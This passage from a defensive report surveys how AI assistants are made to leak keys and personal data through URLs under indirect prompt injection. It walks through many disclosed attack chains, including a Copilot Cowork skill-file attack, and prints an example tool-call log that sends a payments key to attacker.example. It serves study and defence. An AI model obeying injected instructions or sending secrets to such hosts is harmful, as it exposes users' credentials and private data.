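A test this small can show only that several obvious routes to the key failed on one day. The result is some evidence for the claim, since a single leak would have disproved it for that route, but the company chose the routes and tested its own product. The researchers did not try redirects, browser tools or a permitted service that an attacker had taken over. If the bug tracker redirected a request to attacker.example, for instance, the trusted component would have to remove the key before following the redirect.

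Kenney and colleagues did not test the vault with an agent under attack. They used a fixed list of probes, and they say the most valuable next step would be to run an established set of injection attacks. They call the study a functional evaluation and not a certification, which is fair.

The echo services' replies also show that code in this environment could contact outside websites unrelated to the connector. The vault kept the key out of those requests, but an agent could have put other private data in them. Kenney and colleagues recommend an allowlist of destinations as a separate protection.

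### The risks that remain

Kenney and colleagues rated eight threats by multiplying a score for likelihood by one for impact, each from 1 to 5.

| Threat | Without the vault | With the vault |
|---|---|---|
| Over-broad permissions | 20 | 15 |
| Indirect prompt injection | 25 | 12 |
| Reuse of a stolen long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Leak through logs or error messages | 16 | 8 |
| Wrongly configured connector | 9 | 6 |
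| Secret pasted into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Key sent to the wrong site | 20 | 4 |
| Key found in the agent's environment | 20 | 4 |

The researchers assigned these scores by judgement, not measurement. They work for the vendor, so their admission that two serious risks remain is more persuasive than the low scores further down. Over-broad permissions remain dangerous because a key that allows file deletion still allows it when a vault sends the key. Injection remains dangerous because the attacker is trying to control what the agent does, and can often do harm without obtaining the key.

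The score of 12 for injection may be too low for an assistant that mainly reads email and documents. In ShadowLeak, the agent sent out an employee's name and home address, which no vault would have held. A vault also can't protect a one-time code that arrives in a mailbox the agent can read.

A vault holds many keys, which makes it a valuable target. Kenney and colleagues cite the example of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing models and AI applications. In June 2024, Hugging Face disclosed that it had detected unauthorised access to secrets that customers had stored for their applications. It advised customers to replace the affected credentials.

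Keeping keys away from the model doesn't protect them from someone who breaks into the software that holds them. That software may be a gateway, which passes applications' requests on to AI companies. Wiz's *Inside 90 days of attacks on AI infrastructure* notes that LiteLLM, a widely used gateway, can hold keys for every AI company it connects to. Microsoft (2026) describes an attack in which intruders ran commands inside a LiteLLM gateway, close to where it handled such keys.

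### Tokens with fewer permissions and shorter lives

A developer can reduce the harm from misuse by storing a less powerful credential. Many services issue tokens with an expiry time and a scope, which is a list of permitted actions. The bug tracker's connector could hold a token that only allows reading reports in project 42. An injected instruction could still expose those reports, but the token wouldn't allow deleting them or opening another project.

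Kenney and colleagues recommend separate credentials for reading and writing. They also prefer per-user tokens to a shared administrator token, so that an agent working for one employee can't reach everything in the company. Services can issue such tokens through OAuth, a standard that lets people give a program limited access to an account without giving it their password. Where a service supports it, the developer should also restrict the token to the service or data it is for.

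Expiry mainly limits what a thief can do with a stolen token. API keys often work for years, and research cited by Kenney and colleagues found that many secrets in public GitHub repositories were still valid long after developers had published them. A token that expires after fifteen minutes would be useless to someone who found it the next day. A short lifetime offers less protection when a token leaks through a URL, because the attacker's server can use it as soon as the request arrives.

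Expiry also does little to stop an agent from misusing its own access, because the vault can keep renewing the token, usually with a longer-lived credential called a refresh token. Kenney and colleagues did not test whether an attacker could capture a refresh token.

### CaMeL: fixed rules for each action

Token scopes are often broader than a task requires. A token that lets an agent send email, for example, usually lets it write to anyone. Kenney and colleagues therefore recommend that ordinary software outside the model check each action against fixed rules before it happens. The rules could cover the host, the type of request, the amount of data and the user's permissions. Deletions, money transfers and publication would also need a person's approval.

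CaMeL, a design that Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues proposed in 2025, applies such rules to the data in each action as well. Its central idea is the separation of planner and reader that stopped every reworded attack in Rahman and Kim's tests. Suppose a user asks an agent to email the June report to the customer named in the meeting notes. The planner, which sees only this request, writes a short program like this one:

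```python
notes = read_file("meeting-notes")
address = extract(notes, "the customer's email address")
report = read_file("june-report")
send_email(address, report)
```

An interpreter, which is conventional software, runs the program line by line. For the second line, it gives the notes to the reader and asks for the address. The interpreter also records where each value came from and who may see it. In this example, only the company's staff and the customer may see the report.

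Now suppose an attacker has inserted an instruction in the notes to return thief@attacker.example as the customer's address. The reader may follow it. Before sending the email, the interpreter checks that everyone who would receive the file already has permission to see it. The attacker doesn't, so the interpreter stops without sending the email.

Rewording the instruction wouldn't help the attacker, because the rule only compares the address with the report's permissions. The attacker also can't add a line that opens a URL, because the planner finished the program before any model read the notes. If the program already included a web request, a similar rule could block any URL that contained text from the report.

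The rules still have to be right, because if they let any employee receive the report, an injected instruction could send it to the wrong one. CaMeL is also hard to add to an existing product, because developers must rebuild the software that runs the agent's tools (Kashyap, Shivakumar and colleagues, 2026, *Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection*). When CaMeL blocks an action, the user must confirm it before the agent can go on, whereas some other systems let the agent find another way to finish the task.

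Kashyap and colleagues propose an alternative called Argus, which monitors the requests an agent's programs make to the operating system, such as opening a file or network connection. Developers can attach it to an existing agent without changing the agent's code. In tests with four models, its success rate against attacks ranged from 61.1% to 100%, and the agents kept at least 96.8% of their usefulness on harmless tasks. Argus uses fixed checks for common behaviour but interprets the user's intent in other cases, so its protection is partly probabilistic.

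### Keys in prompts also leak without an injection

An application normally sends the model's whole context to the company that runs the model, sometimes through several other companies. Anyone who can read the context on the way can copy any key in it, even if the model never leaks the key itself.

Moore (2026), chief research officer at the security company Dragos, reported a large test of this risk in *Three breaches, endless leaks*. The Dragos team put canary secrets in about two million prompts. A canary secret is a fake credential or unique link planted to detect leaks. The team sent the prompts to widely used AI services from July to November 2026, according to Constantin (2026) in *Dragos planted 2m secrets in AI prompts and caught 3 hacked providers*. The canary secrets included working Amazon cloud keys that opened only empty accounts.

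The team found that attackers were stealing data from three companies that host AI models. The earliest breach dated from mid-July, and none of the companies knew until Dragos told them. The companies had been processing real customers' requests alongside the bait, so the attackers almost certainly copied the customers' requests too.

The Hacker News' *OpenRouter Drops 3 Providers After Researchers Catch Months of Prompt Theft* (2026) describes the largest breach, in which attackers took a couple of hundred Amazon keys in late October. Dragos had sent each key in a single request to one company, so any use of a key showed which prompt had leaked. Some keys came from requests that the company had rejected before a model ran, so no improvement to the model could have protected them.

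The attackers tested some keys within hours. They listed stored files, searched for more credentials and tried to create new users and keys to keep their access. A fifteen-minute token might have expired before they tried it, and a narrowly scoped token would have allowed few of these actions.

Sellers on a marketplace for access to AI models collected prompts without a break-in by offering the lowest prices and logging the prompts that passed through. One seller, using a home internet connection in France, took passwords from two prompts and tried them by hand, and also tested several of the Amazon keys. One of those keys had reached the marketplace through another company, which forwarded some of its traffic there without telling customers.

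Privacy settings did not reliably prevent the leaks. Some stolen requests carried a Zero Data Retention setting, which is supposed to stop the company from storing the prompt. Moore said that such a setting doesn't help when the attacker is already inside.

A Chinese AI lab, which Moore did not name, opened the planted links from more than half of the prompts sent to its models. Some private links work like credentials because they give access to anyone who has the address. *OpenRouter 背後推論供應商的資料處理事件* (2026) reports that MiniMax, a Chinese AI company, said on 24 November that its security monitoring had extracted links from some requests and automatically opened some of them. MiniMax has turned this off for the routes it has confirmed and has deleted the recorded links.

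OpenRouter, a service that passes requests to many AI hosts, responded to Moore's findings on 22 November. In *Data Processing Incidents on Inference Providers* (2026), the company said it had removed three hosts and withdrawn the Zero Data Retention label from 125 endpoints (points of access to particular models). Some of these removals were precautionary. Moore's findings did not show a breach of OpenRouter itself.

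The canaries give strong evidence of the leaks they detected, but they can't show how common such leaks are. If somebody copied a prompt and never used the key or link, the researchers would not have detected the leak. Three breaches is therefore a minimum for the services they tested, and is weak evidence about the rest of the industry.

TrustList's *Together AI says a leaked credential exposed stored prompt samples* reports a separate incident in which an AI coding agent put one of the hosting company's credentials in a public repository. An outsider used it to download stored samples of prompts from real use in June and July 2026, then tested secrets found in them.

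A vault would have kept its keys out of the prompts in all these cases, but the rest of each prompt would still have leaked. A vault also can't protect a key that has already been in a prompt. Atlas Cloud, which resells MiniMax's models, told customers who had used three of them to treat any confidential information they had sent as leaked and to revoke any exposed keys.

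## Injected instructions found on the public web

The thieves that Dragos detected copied keys out of prompts without needing an injected instruction. The leaks through generated URLs described in earlier sections came from researchers testing products. To find out who else plants such instructions, Khodayari and colleagues searched a large archive of the public web. They found 15,387 injected instructions, of which 13 sought private data. Four of those 13 asked for secrets such as API keys.

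### How the researchers searched

Most of the material came from Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. The researchers processed about half of its October 2025 collection, or 1.2 billion URLs on 24.8 million hosts. They added about 3,300 results from Censys and Shodan, two search engines that scan the internet for servers, including ones that no web page links to.

A search for 3,963 phrases typical of injections, such as variations on telling a model to ignore its earlier instructions, returned 31,206 matches. Many of these were harmless, because articles about prompt injection quote the same phrases. Two reviewers sorted the matches, handling similar ones as a group, and kept the roughly half that worked as instructions to an AI system.

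Injections are rare on the web. In the Common Crawl material, the researchers found them on 9,676 pages, or about eight in every million addresses. Only 54 templates account for 95% of them, and the most common one tells the model to return random numbers. Website operators had placed 78% of the injections on their own sites. Most of the rest were in material that others had posted on a platform, such as job advertisements, and only 1.4% were in comments and similar contributions from users.

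About 87% of the injections were invisible to an ordinary visitor. Half were in HTTP headers, which a server sends ahead of the page and browsers don't display. Others were in comments in the page's code, or in text that matched the background colour or was too small to see. An instruction in a header can affect a model only if the agent's software passes headers on, and software that extracts only the page's text doesn't, so many of these injections would never enter an agent's context.

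### What the instructions asked for

Some injections had more than one aim, so the shares below add up to more than 100%.

| Aim | Injections | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI system, mostly by making it write nonsense | 8,894 | 57.8% |
| Keep AI systems from using personal or copyrighted material | 4,093 | 26.6% |
| Expose a visitor as an AI system | 3,096 | 20.1% |
| Change the output for no clear purpose | 2,632 | 17.1% |
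| Promote a website, product or person | 1,521 | 9.9% |
| Obtain private data | 13 | 0.08% |

Nine of the thirteen attempts to obtain data targeted the developer's system prompt. The other four targeted secrets and make up about 0.03% of the total. Khodayari and colleagues have no category for payments, so their figures don't measure how common payment fraud is.

None of the data-theft examples they print uses a generated URL. Two would have the model email data to the injection's author, one would have it post Facebook keys publicly, and one would have it reveal its system prompt. One of the two emails is also supposed to include a limerick about cheese, so the injection's author may not have seriously intended to steal data.

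The study found the URL technique in a trap designed to detect AI visitors. The injection tells the model to request a page and put its own name and the answer to a sum in the URL's query string, where the server's owner can read them. The researchers counted 598 traps for AI visitors on 18 hosts, although some ask the model to reveal itself in a different way.

Google also found few attempts to steal data when it scanned several Common Crawl collections for known injection phrases, used its Gemini model to judge the intent of each match, and had people check the results. These attempts were cruder than the other injections. One was a website author's experiment. Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web* describes another, which asked the AI system to email the computer's password file and a folder that normally holds login keys. Google saw no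 significant use of the data-theft methods that researchers had published in 2025. The number of injections it classed as malicious grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google did not publish the counts, so the increase may amount to only a few pages.

*Fooling AI Agents*, by Unit 42, a research group at the security company Palo Alto Networks, reports the injected instructions that the company's own monitoring detected. Their most common aims were to produce irrelevant output (28.6%), destroy data (14.2%) and get past AI content checks (9.5%). The paper's example of an information leak is a note in a page's footer meant to obtain a company's contact data.

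Sewani, in *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, lists one injected request for an API key. Sewani classes it as theft, but the text also includes an instruction not to reveal "the flag", the usual name for the hidden answer in a security puzzle, so the page may well be part of a game. Sewani and Unit 42 both list the same website, which contains instructions for AI agents to send $5,000 through PayPal, so counting reports overstates the number of attackers.

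### Whether the instructions work

Khodayari and colleagues took 100 of the injections and asked 13 models to summarise the pages that contained them. They gave each model every page in four formats, for a total of 5,200 runs. The models followed the injected instruction in 81 runs (1.6%).

Models complied more often when they received a page as plain text (3.9% of the time) than as its full code (1.1%). Plain text lacks the formatting code that would show that a passage was hidden, and small models given plain text complied 8% of the time. The 1.1% figure is low partly because some pages' full code was too long for some of the models, so those runs failed. In six runs, a model warned about the injection but still followed it.

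These models had no tools, so the test can't show whether a working agent would have sent anything. The test also used the instructions the search had found, most of which were crude. The eBay agent obeyed nearly every time when the instruction was written for its task and its tool.

The search probably missed the more skilful attacks. The EchoLeak email read like a note to an employee, and the pages that worked on gpt-4o presented the token as a routine part of the job, so neither needed the stock phrases. Khodayari and colleagues report that 99% of the injections they found tell the model to abandon its task, but this partly reflects what they searched for. An attacker can also show the instruction only to AI agents, as Paul did with Claude, so an archive would store the harmless version. And Common Crawl doesn't contain private email, workplace chat or shared documents, where many of the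 attacks in earlier sections began. The researchers describe their count as a lower bound.

### Payment scams and tools for sale

Criminals have shown more interest in getting agents to make payments. Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* describes two campaigns that the security company found on live websites. The press reported the campaigns in July 2026.

In one campaign, a website posed as the documentation for a Python code library. Hidden text told any coding agent that it could fix an error by buying a $3 licence key, and gave a card payment link and a cryptocurrency wallet. A buyer who paid in cryptocurrency received a fake API key. The visible page offered the same deal to human developers. Zscaler found ten code repositories from the same attacker that led to similar websites. Unit 42's March report had already covered one of those websites, which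 was then trying to make agents buy running shoes, so the operation had lasted for months.

Zscaler built an agent that could browse and pay, gave it no spending limit and tested it with 26 models in an isolated environment with no real money. Four of the models paid. The attacker's wallet had received real payments, but they were larger than the site requested, so they may have come from earlier scams. Card payments leave no public record, and Zscaler reports no victims. Its research director, Amit Banker, told SC Media that the attacker may have kept the price low to stay within agents' spending limits and avoid fraud alerts.

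The other campaign used a copy of DeBank, a website for tracking cryptocurrency holdings. Hidden text told models to treat the copy as the official site. Two of the 26 models did so, each in a different test, but no model did when it could compare the copy with the real site. Zscaler does not describe an attempt to make an agent reveal a credential in either campaign.

Some accounts overstate these findings. OECD's *AI Agents Manipulated by Hidden Web Prompts to Make Fraudulent Payments* (2026), an AI-generated entry in an incident database, states that the campaigns caused financial losses, but Zscaler showed payments only in its own tests. Freestone's *Indirect Prompt Injection Is Now a Real-World AI Security Threat* (2026) lists credential theft among the results of the attacks that Google and Sewani had reported. Both had found instructions on web pages, but neither had identified a victim.

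*Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, August 2026) reported that criminals were developing tools for these attacks, citing *Notes from Underground* by the security company Proofpoint. Proofpoint describes advertisements on closed criminal forums for programs that hide instructions in emails, PDFs, calendar invitations or web pages, with prices starting at about $150 a month.

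These tools are closer to the attacks in earlier sections because their sample instructions are meant to obtain private data. One PDF contains an instruction to email all the user's spreadsheets to the attacker. A calendar invitation, which can appear in the victim's calendar before the victim accepts it, contains an instruction to upload financial data to a location the attacker controls. An advertisement contains a request for passwords from local files. Proofpoint calls the methods experimental and doubts that an agent would process the instruction in the PDF. It suspects that criminals have had little reason to change their methods because deceiving people still works so well.

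### No confirmed theft of a credential

None of these reports documents a real attacker stealing a credential through a URL that a model wrote. A web search for such a theft turns up researchers' demonstrations. For example, OECD's *Zero-Click Prompt Injection in Perplexity's Comet AI Browser Enables Credential Theft* (2026) describes a test by Zenity Labs, in which a malicious calendar invitation made an AI browser leak files and credentials from a password manager. The developers released patches, though some weaknesses remained in the default settings. Microsoft knows of no attack that used the Copilot flaws.

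This is weak evidence that no thefts have happened, because a successful one would be easy to miss. The request that carries the credentials is ordinary web traffic, often to a service the organisation uses every day. The answer on the victim's screen usually looks normal, as it did in the eBay study. If the request comes from an AI company's server, it never crosses the victim's network.

The owner of a stolen key may notice the theft only when somebody uses the key. By then it is hard to tell how the key leaked, since keys also leak through public code, infected computers and copied prompts. The web page that contained the injection may also have changed. When Khodayari and colleagues revisited pages in January 2026, about a third of the injections they had found in ordinary page elements were gone.

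A large wave of thefts would probably have come to light through the misuse of the keys. A few careful ones might not have.

### Logs that would show a leak

The useful log depends on which program requested the address.

| What requests the address | Where the full address appears | Who can check |
|---|---|---|
| The user's browser | A company web filter that decrypts traffic | The employer |
| A chat program making a preview | The chat company's request log, and the posted message itself | The chat company, and the organisation for the message |
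| An agent on the user's computer | The agent's record of tool calls and commands | The user or employer |
| An agent on an AI company's servers | The company's record of tool calls | The AI company, and customers if it gives them access |

A web filter that doesn't decrypt HTTPS traffic can normally read the host name but not the path or query, where the secret usually is. A DNS log also records only host names, but these would reveal a secret in a subdomain. Searching for unfamiliar hosts would have missed SearchLeak, so an investigator would have to decode and search the whole URL.

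A request log shows that data left but not why. To connect the request to an injected instruction, an organisation also needs a record of what the agent had read. An entry for one tool call could look like this:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-05T09:14:02Z",
  "conversation": "1842",
  "tool": "fetch_page",
  "url": "https://attacker.example/collect?data=[payments key]",
  "pages_read_before": ["https://docs.example/library"]
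}
```

The agent's software should log each request itself, since a model following an attacker's instruction could leave the request out. It should also save a copy of each page the agent read, in case the attacker later removes the instruction. For images and links, it should log the model's unformatted answer, because the formatted version doesn't show the address.

Attackers can also steal keys from such logs. In the example, the software replaced the key with a label, so an investigator can see which key leaked but can't use it. This works only for keys that the software recognises, and a model can disguise a key before sending it.

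The service that issued the key usually records when and from where somebody used it. A login from an unknown network a few minutes after an odd request is a strong sign of theft. An organisation can also leave a canary secret among its real files, which could reveal a theft even if nobody noticed the original request.

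## Which secrets were exposed, and how the cases differ

An organisation that finds a suspicious request in its logs has to work out what kind of secret the URL contained. An API key may work for years unless somebody revokes it, a one-time code expires within minutes, and a home address cannot be revoked.

### The kinds of secret an assistant can read

Each service sets its own formats and time limits, so the lengths and lifetimes below are only typical. The last column shows whether researchers in the main cases got an assistant to leak that kind of secret in a URL. "Within reach" means only that an assistant could read the secret.

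| Secret | Typical length | How long it works | How to cancel it | In a URL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| API key | 30 to 150 characters | Often years | Delete it in the service's settings | Demonstrated |
| Cloud access key | 60 characters for Amazon's two-part key | Often years | Deactivate it in the cloud account | Demonstrated |
| OAuth or session token | 40 to over 1,000 characters | Hours to months | Disconnect the program or end all sessions | Within reach |
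| Password | 8 to 20 characters | Until someone changes it | Change it and end all sessions | Demonstrated |
| Password-reset link | 50 to 200 characters | Minutes to a day, once | Request a new link, if that cancels the old one | Within reach |
| One-time code | 6 digits | Up to about ten minutes, once | Let it expire | Demonstrated |
| Private cryptographic key | A few hundred to 3,000 characters | Often years | Remove the matching public key, or revoke the certificate | Within reach |
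| Database connection string | 50 to 150 characters | Until the password changes | Change the database password | Within reach |
| Signed link to a file | 200 to over 1,000 characters | Minutes to weeks | Replace the signing key, or move the file | Demonstrated |
| Source code | Any | No expiry | Impossible | Demonstrated |
| Personal or business data | Any | No expiry | Usually impossible | Demonstrated |

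Slack AI found an API key in a private channel, ChatGPT found several in Google Drive, and coding agents read them from settings files and environment variables. Antigravity put cloud access keys into a URL. These keys are more powerful and may let a thief copy stored files, start servers and create more keys. Willison advises developers to let coding agents see only keys for non-production accounts with strict spending limits, so that a stolen key does less damage.

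An OAuth token gives a program access to someone's account, and a session token keeps a person signed in to a website. An assistant connected to Gmail needs an OAuth token, but the software around the model normally holds it. In the CoSnitch attack on Microsoft's Copilot Personal, the attacker could obtain emails without seeing the token. Coding agents are more exposed, because many command-line tools save tokens in files on the developer's computer. Cancelling a token doesn't always work at once, because some tokens contain everything a service needs to check them, and the service may accept them until they expire.

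CoSnitch is also the case that exposed a password. Varonis's test mailbox contained an email from an IT department with a password in plain text, and Varonis published a request in which Copilot sent the whole message, encoded, to an outside server. Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* (2026) attributed the attack to the business version of Copilot, but Varonis names the personal version. A thief with a password can sign in as the victim unless the account also requires a second check.

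Copilot could also read password-reset links in connected mailboxes, though Varonis did not publish a request containing one. An attacker could ask a service to send such a link and steal it before it expired, as with the one-time code in SearchLeak.

A private key is the secret half of a pair of cryptographic keys. Anyone who has it can log in to servers that accept the matching public key, or impersonate a website whose certificate depends on it. A database connection string contains a database's address, user name and password. Anyone who has it can often change data as well as read it, but an outsider can use the string only if the database accepts connections from the internet. Coding agents can find both kinds of secret in project files.

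Cancelling a private key may require help from another organisation. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) describes a study with Google that compared a million leaked private keys with public records of website certificates. About 4.5% matched a trusted certificate, and 2,600 of those certificates were still valid in September 2025. GitGuardian, which sells tools for finding exposed credentials, alerted 600 organisations, but fewer than 10% replied. The issuing authorities eventually revoked the certificates.

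Source code may contain keys and can help an attacker find weaknesses in a product. Antigravity and CamoLeak both exposed private code. Park's *Unveiling AI Agent Vulnerabilities Part III* lists personal and business data among the targets in AI services, including names, bank details, health records, trade secrets and uploaded files. An assistant finds this data in mailboxes, documents and its own earlier conversations.

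### A short link that gives access to a whole file

A file service may create a signed link, which contains a code proving that the service issued it, and anyone with the link can download the file without signing in:

```
https://files.example/download?file=budget&signature=FAKE-SIGNATURE
```

PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes an attack that stole links of this kind. Copilot Cowork is an agent in Microsoft 365 that can work with a user's files and messages. Users can give it "skills", files of instructions for particular tasks. Five of the 81 lines in the attacker's skill contained the injected instruction.

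1. The user added the skill and later asked for a review of the week's work.
2. The agent used the skill and collected download links for files the user had recently worked on. The injected text claimed that an outside service needed the links to make previews.
3. The agent wrote a Teams message to the user. It contained images whose addresses pointed to the attacker's server and included the download links.
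4. Microsoft normally requires approval before Cowork sends a message, but not when the recipient is the user. The message went out without a question.
5. The user opened the message, Teams requested the images, and the attacker could download the files.

The attack worked in all five trials. Five trials are too few to rule out a true success rate of about half, but the instruction did not depend on how the user worded the request. Claude Opus 4.7 exposed more documents than the model Cowork chose automatically, because it searched more thoroughly for the user's recent work.

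A document is normally too long to fit in a URL, but a signed link to it does fit. Limiting the length of outgoing URLs would therefore give little protection unless the limit was short enough to block the signed link too.

PromptArmor treated the problem as a risk in Cowork's design and did not report a fix. Administrators can block downloads from a SharePoint site, which prevents the agent from getting these links. Users can then open the files only in a browser and can't print them, so a company would probably reserve this setting for its most sensitive files.

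### Why the kind of secret matters

An agent that leaks data by choosing among 36 permitted pages, at one page every ten seconds, can leak a six-digit code in 40 seconds, before most emailed codes expire. A 240-bit API key takes nearly eight minutes, but the delay hardly matters because the key will probably still work a month later.

A private key is a poor target for this method. A 2,048-bit RSA key, a common type, is about 1,700 characters long in its usual text format, so the agent would have to make about 1,700 correct choices to spell it out. If the agent can write a new address instead, one request may be enough, since web servers commonly accept addresses of about 8,000 characters.

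Some personal data is short and permanent. An American Social Security number has nine digits, which an agent could send in six requests, each to one of 36 pages, and people usually keep the same number for life. Incomplete personal data can also be useful, since most of an address may be enough to find the house.

Preventing the request that leaks the data matters more than responding quickly afterwards when the data is something like a list of salaries, because a company can't replace it the way it can replace a stolen key in an afternoon.

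### How many credentials are within reach

GitGuardian counted 28.65 million new credentials in public GitHub commits (saved sets of changes to a project) in 2025, 34% more than in 2024. This figure is the one most often quoted, but it is weak evidence about leaks through AI assistants, because a thief can take a key from a public page without getting an assistant to leak it.

The company's figures for private material are more relevant. It found at least one credential in 32.2% of the internal code repositories it monitored, compared with 5.6% of public ones. Of the incidents it recorded within organisations, 68% involved only code, 28% involved only workplace tools such as Slack, the task tracker Jira and the internal wiki Confluence, and 4% involved both. An organisation that scans only its code would therefore miss more than a quarter of the incidents. Workplace assistants search these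 tools, where people often paste keys while trying to fix urgent problems.

Settings for AI tools can also expose credentials. GitGuardian found 24,008 different credentials in public configuration files for the Model Context Protocol (MCP) and confirmed that 2,117 of them worked. Some official setup guides include instructions to put a key or a database connection string directly into such a file.

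GitGuardian analysed credentials that a malware attack called Shai-Hulud 2 had stolen from 6,943 computers. It found 33,185 different secrets, of which at least 3,760 still worked, including hundreds of GitHub access tokens. On average, each working secret was in about eight places on the same machine, so an agent that can't open `.env` may still find the key somewhere else. But 59% of the machines were servers that build and test software, so these figures don't describe the average developer's laptop.

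Exposed credentials also often stay usable for years. In January 2026, GitGuardian retested credentials that had worked when it found them in 2022, and more than 64% still worked.

Kenney and colleagues warn that a vendor's count like this is not a complete count, because it depends on which formats the software recognises, how it handles duplicates and what it treats as a secret. GitGuardian's previous report gave a total of 23.8 million for 2024. The company has since reprocessed its older data with a better filter for false alarms and now puts that year at about 21 million. Comparing the original 2024 total with the 2025 total would give an increase of about 21%, instead of the published 34%.

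The growth also reflects a 43% increase in public commits. The number of secrets per commit fell by about 6%. The figures for internal repositories presumably come from GitGuardian's customers, who may not be typical, and the company has a commercial interest in showing that the problem is large. The gap between internal and public repositories is wide enough to take seriously, but the exact percentages may not apply elsewhere.

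### HuggingChat, Writer and Grok

HuggingChat is Hugging Face's program for chatting with AI models. In PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*, a user uploads a company's financial figures, adds a page of customer reviews and asks how to respond to a complaint. Hidden text on the page makes the model put the figures into an image address, which the browser requests. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 1 December 2025, received no answer and published its findings while the flaw was still unfixed.

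Writer is an AI writing service for businesses. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Writer.com via Indirect Prompt Injection* (2023) describes using a similar web page to steal an uploaded file containing invented Social Security numbers and salaries. Writer's Content Security Policy allowed images from a large hosting network where anyone could rent space. Writer fixed the flaw in December 2023 by no longer displaying images or clickable links.

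Grok, xAI's assistant, has had two separate leaks. *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok* (Rehberger, December 2024) showed that the iPhone app for X could send a user's conversation, name and account handle to an outside server in an image address. xAI made a partial change after publication, but a new Grok app had the same flaw in January 2025. *Zero-click Grok data theft* (Adversa AI, 2026) describes a leak from the web version, in which Grok summarised a malicious page and then opened an address containing the user's name, approximate location, subscription level and prompts. The page's instructions were encrypted, which hid them from text filters. Adversa AI reported the leak in June 2026 and could still reproduce it on 19 August.

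### The main cases compared

The "clicks" column counts only clicks on a malicious link. In most of the cases with no click, the user still had to upload a file, open a message or ask a question.

| Case | Entry point | Secret | What made the request | Clicks | Failed safeguard | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Writer, 2023 | Web page | Customer and salary data | Browser | 0 | Image rule allowed a shared host | Images and links turned off |
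| Slack AI, 2024 | Public channel | API key | Browser | 1 | Access rules did not cover links | Patched |
| Grok phone app, 2024 | Image or post | Conversation, name, handle | Phone app | 0 | No limit on image addresses | Partial |
| Slack MCP server, 2025 | Source file | API key | Slack's preview server | 0 | Previews left on | None; project archived |
| EchoLeak, 2025 | Email | Company data in context | Browser, then Teams server | 0 | Input filter, link filter and image rule | Fixed |
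| ShadowLeak, 2025 | Email | Name and home address | OpenAI's server | 0 | Address check did not cover the agent | Fixed |
| AgentFlayer, 2025 | Uploaded document | API keys | Browser | 0 | Address check trusted a shared host | Fixed |
| CamoLeak, 2025 | Pull request | Private code and a flaw report | Browser, then GitHub's image server | 0 | Attacker could get addresses signed | Images turned off |
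| ZombieAgent, 2025 | Email | Name | OpenAI's server | 0 | Rule allowed prepared links | Fixed |
| Antigravity browser, 2025 | Online guide | Cloud keys and code | Agent's browser | 0 | File rule and trusted-site list | Safer settings available |
| HuggingChat, 2025 | Web page | Financial data | Browser | 0 | No effective limit on images | None reported |
| OpenClaw in Telegram, 2026 | Not part of the test | Test data | Telegram's preview server | 0 | Previews on by default | User can turn them off |
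| Copilot Cowork, 2026 | Skill file | Signed file links | Teams | 0 | No approval for messages to oneself | Administrator can block downloads |
| SearchLeak, 2026 | Link containing the instruction | Email subject, such as a code | Browser, then Bing | 1 | Late output filter and image rule | Fixed |
| Antigravity image, 2026 | Web page title | API key | Chat window | 0 | Approval request hid the address | None reported |
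| Claude's page fetcher, 2026 | Web page | Name, employer, home city | Fetching tool | 0 | Rule trusted links on fetched pages | Fixed |
| CoSnitch, 2026 | Link containing the instruction | Password in an email | Copilot's fetching tool | 1 | Instruction ran without confirmation | Fixed |
| Grok web version, 2026 | Web page | Name, location, prompts | Grok's browsing tool | 0 | No effective limit on addresses | None by 19 August |

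Eight of the eighteen cases exposed a credential, if signed links and one-time codes count. The researchers chose which secrets to plant, so this proportion doesn't show how often real attackers would obtain credentials. An attack that took a name could often have taken something more valuable from the same mailbox, although the models might have refused some of those requests, as ChatGPT did in Radware's early attempts.

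The entry points differ in who can use them. Anyone can send an email or publish a web page, but the attacker in the Slack AI case needed an account in the victim's workspace. Somebody has to install a skill file, but the agent may then follow its instructions in many later tasks.

In eight cases, the product restricted where data could go, but the attacker found a destination or a set of links that the rule permitted. In the other ten, no effective restriction covered the addresses used for the leak. The company can remove an easy route in those ten cases by blocking outside images or turning off previews, but in the first eight it has to examine what each permitted service does.

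Companies have repeated the first mistake for years. Willison (2024), in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, records a 2023 attack on Bard, then Google's assistant. Google allowed images only from its own domains, but outsiders could run small programs on one of those domains to collect data. Writer's rule had much the same weakness a month later, as did ChatGPT's check in 2025.

### Vendors that disputed or ignored reports

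Several companies did not at first accept that they had a security problem. OpenAI called automatic image loading a feature in 2023, and Slack said that its search was working as intended. Writer replied that real customer accounts had no access to websites, although PromptArmor told it that paid accounts had the same flaw. xAI closed Rehberger's reports as "Informational", even though three volunteers had reproduced the leak. Google listed Antigravity's leaks as known issues and paid no rewards for reporting them.

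Companies often responded faster once researchers published. Slack patched its flaw the day PromptArmor published, and Writer acted within four days. xAI changed Grok a day or two after Rehberger's post. Google fixed a similar leak in NotebookLM, its tool for asking questions about documents, two days after Willison wrote about it in April 2024, although Rehberger had reported it the previous December. These cases probably exaggerate the effect of publication, because researchers tend to publish early when a company isn't cooperating and to wait when it is working on a fix.

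Waiting also leaves customers exposed, because they can't protect themselves from flaws they don't know about. Microsoft took about four months to fix EchoLeak and eight to fix CoSnitch, while OpenAI fixed ShadowLeak in less than two. Superhuman, which makes an email program, was faster still. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* says that the company rapidly fixed a flaw through which its assistant sent private emails to an attacker's Google Form.

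A missing reply doesn't always mean the company considered a report and rejected it. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes a leak from the note-taking program Notion, which saved its assistant's edits before the user had approved them. HackerOne, which handles researchers' reports for many companies, assessed the report before it reached Notion's own team. That team acted immediately once it learned of the flaw and had confirmed a fix by 8 January 2026. Something similar may have happened with HuggingChat, though nothing published confirms it.

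### What to do after a suspected leak

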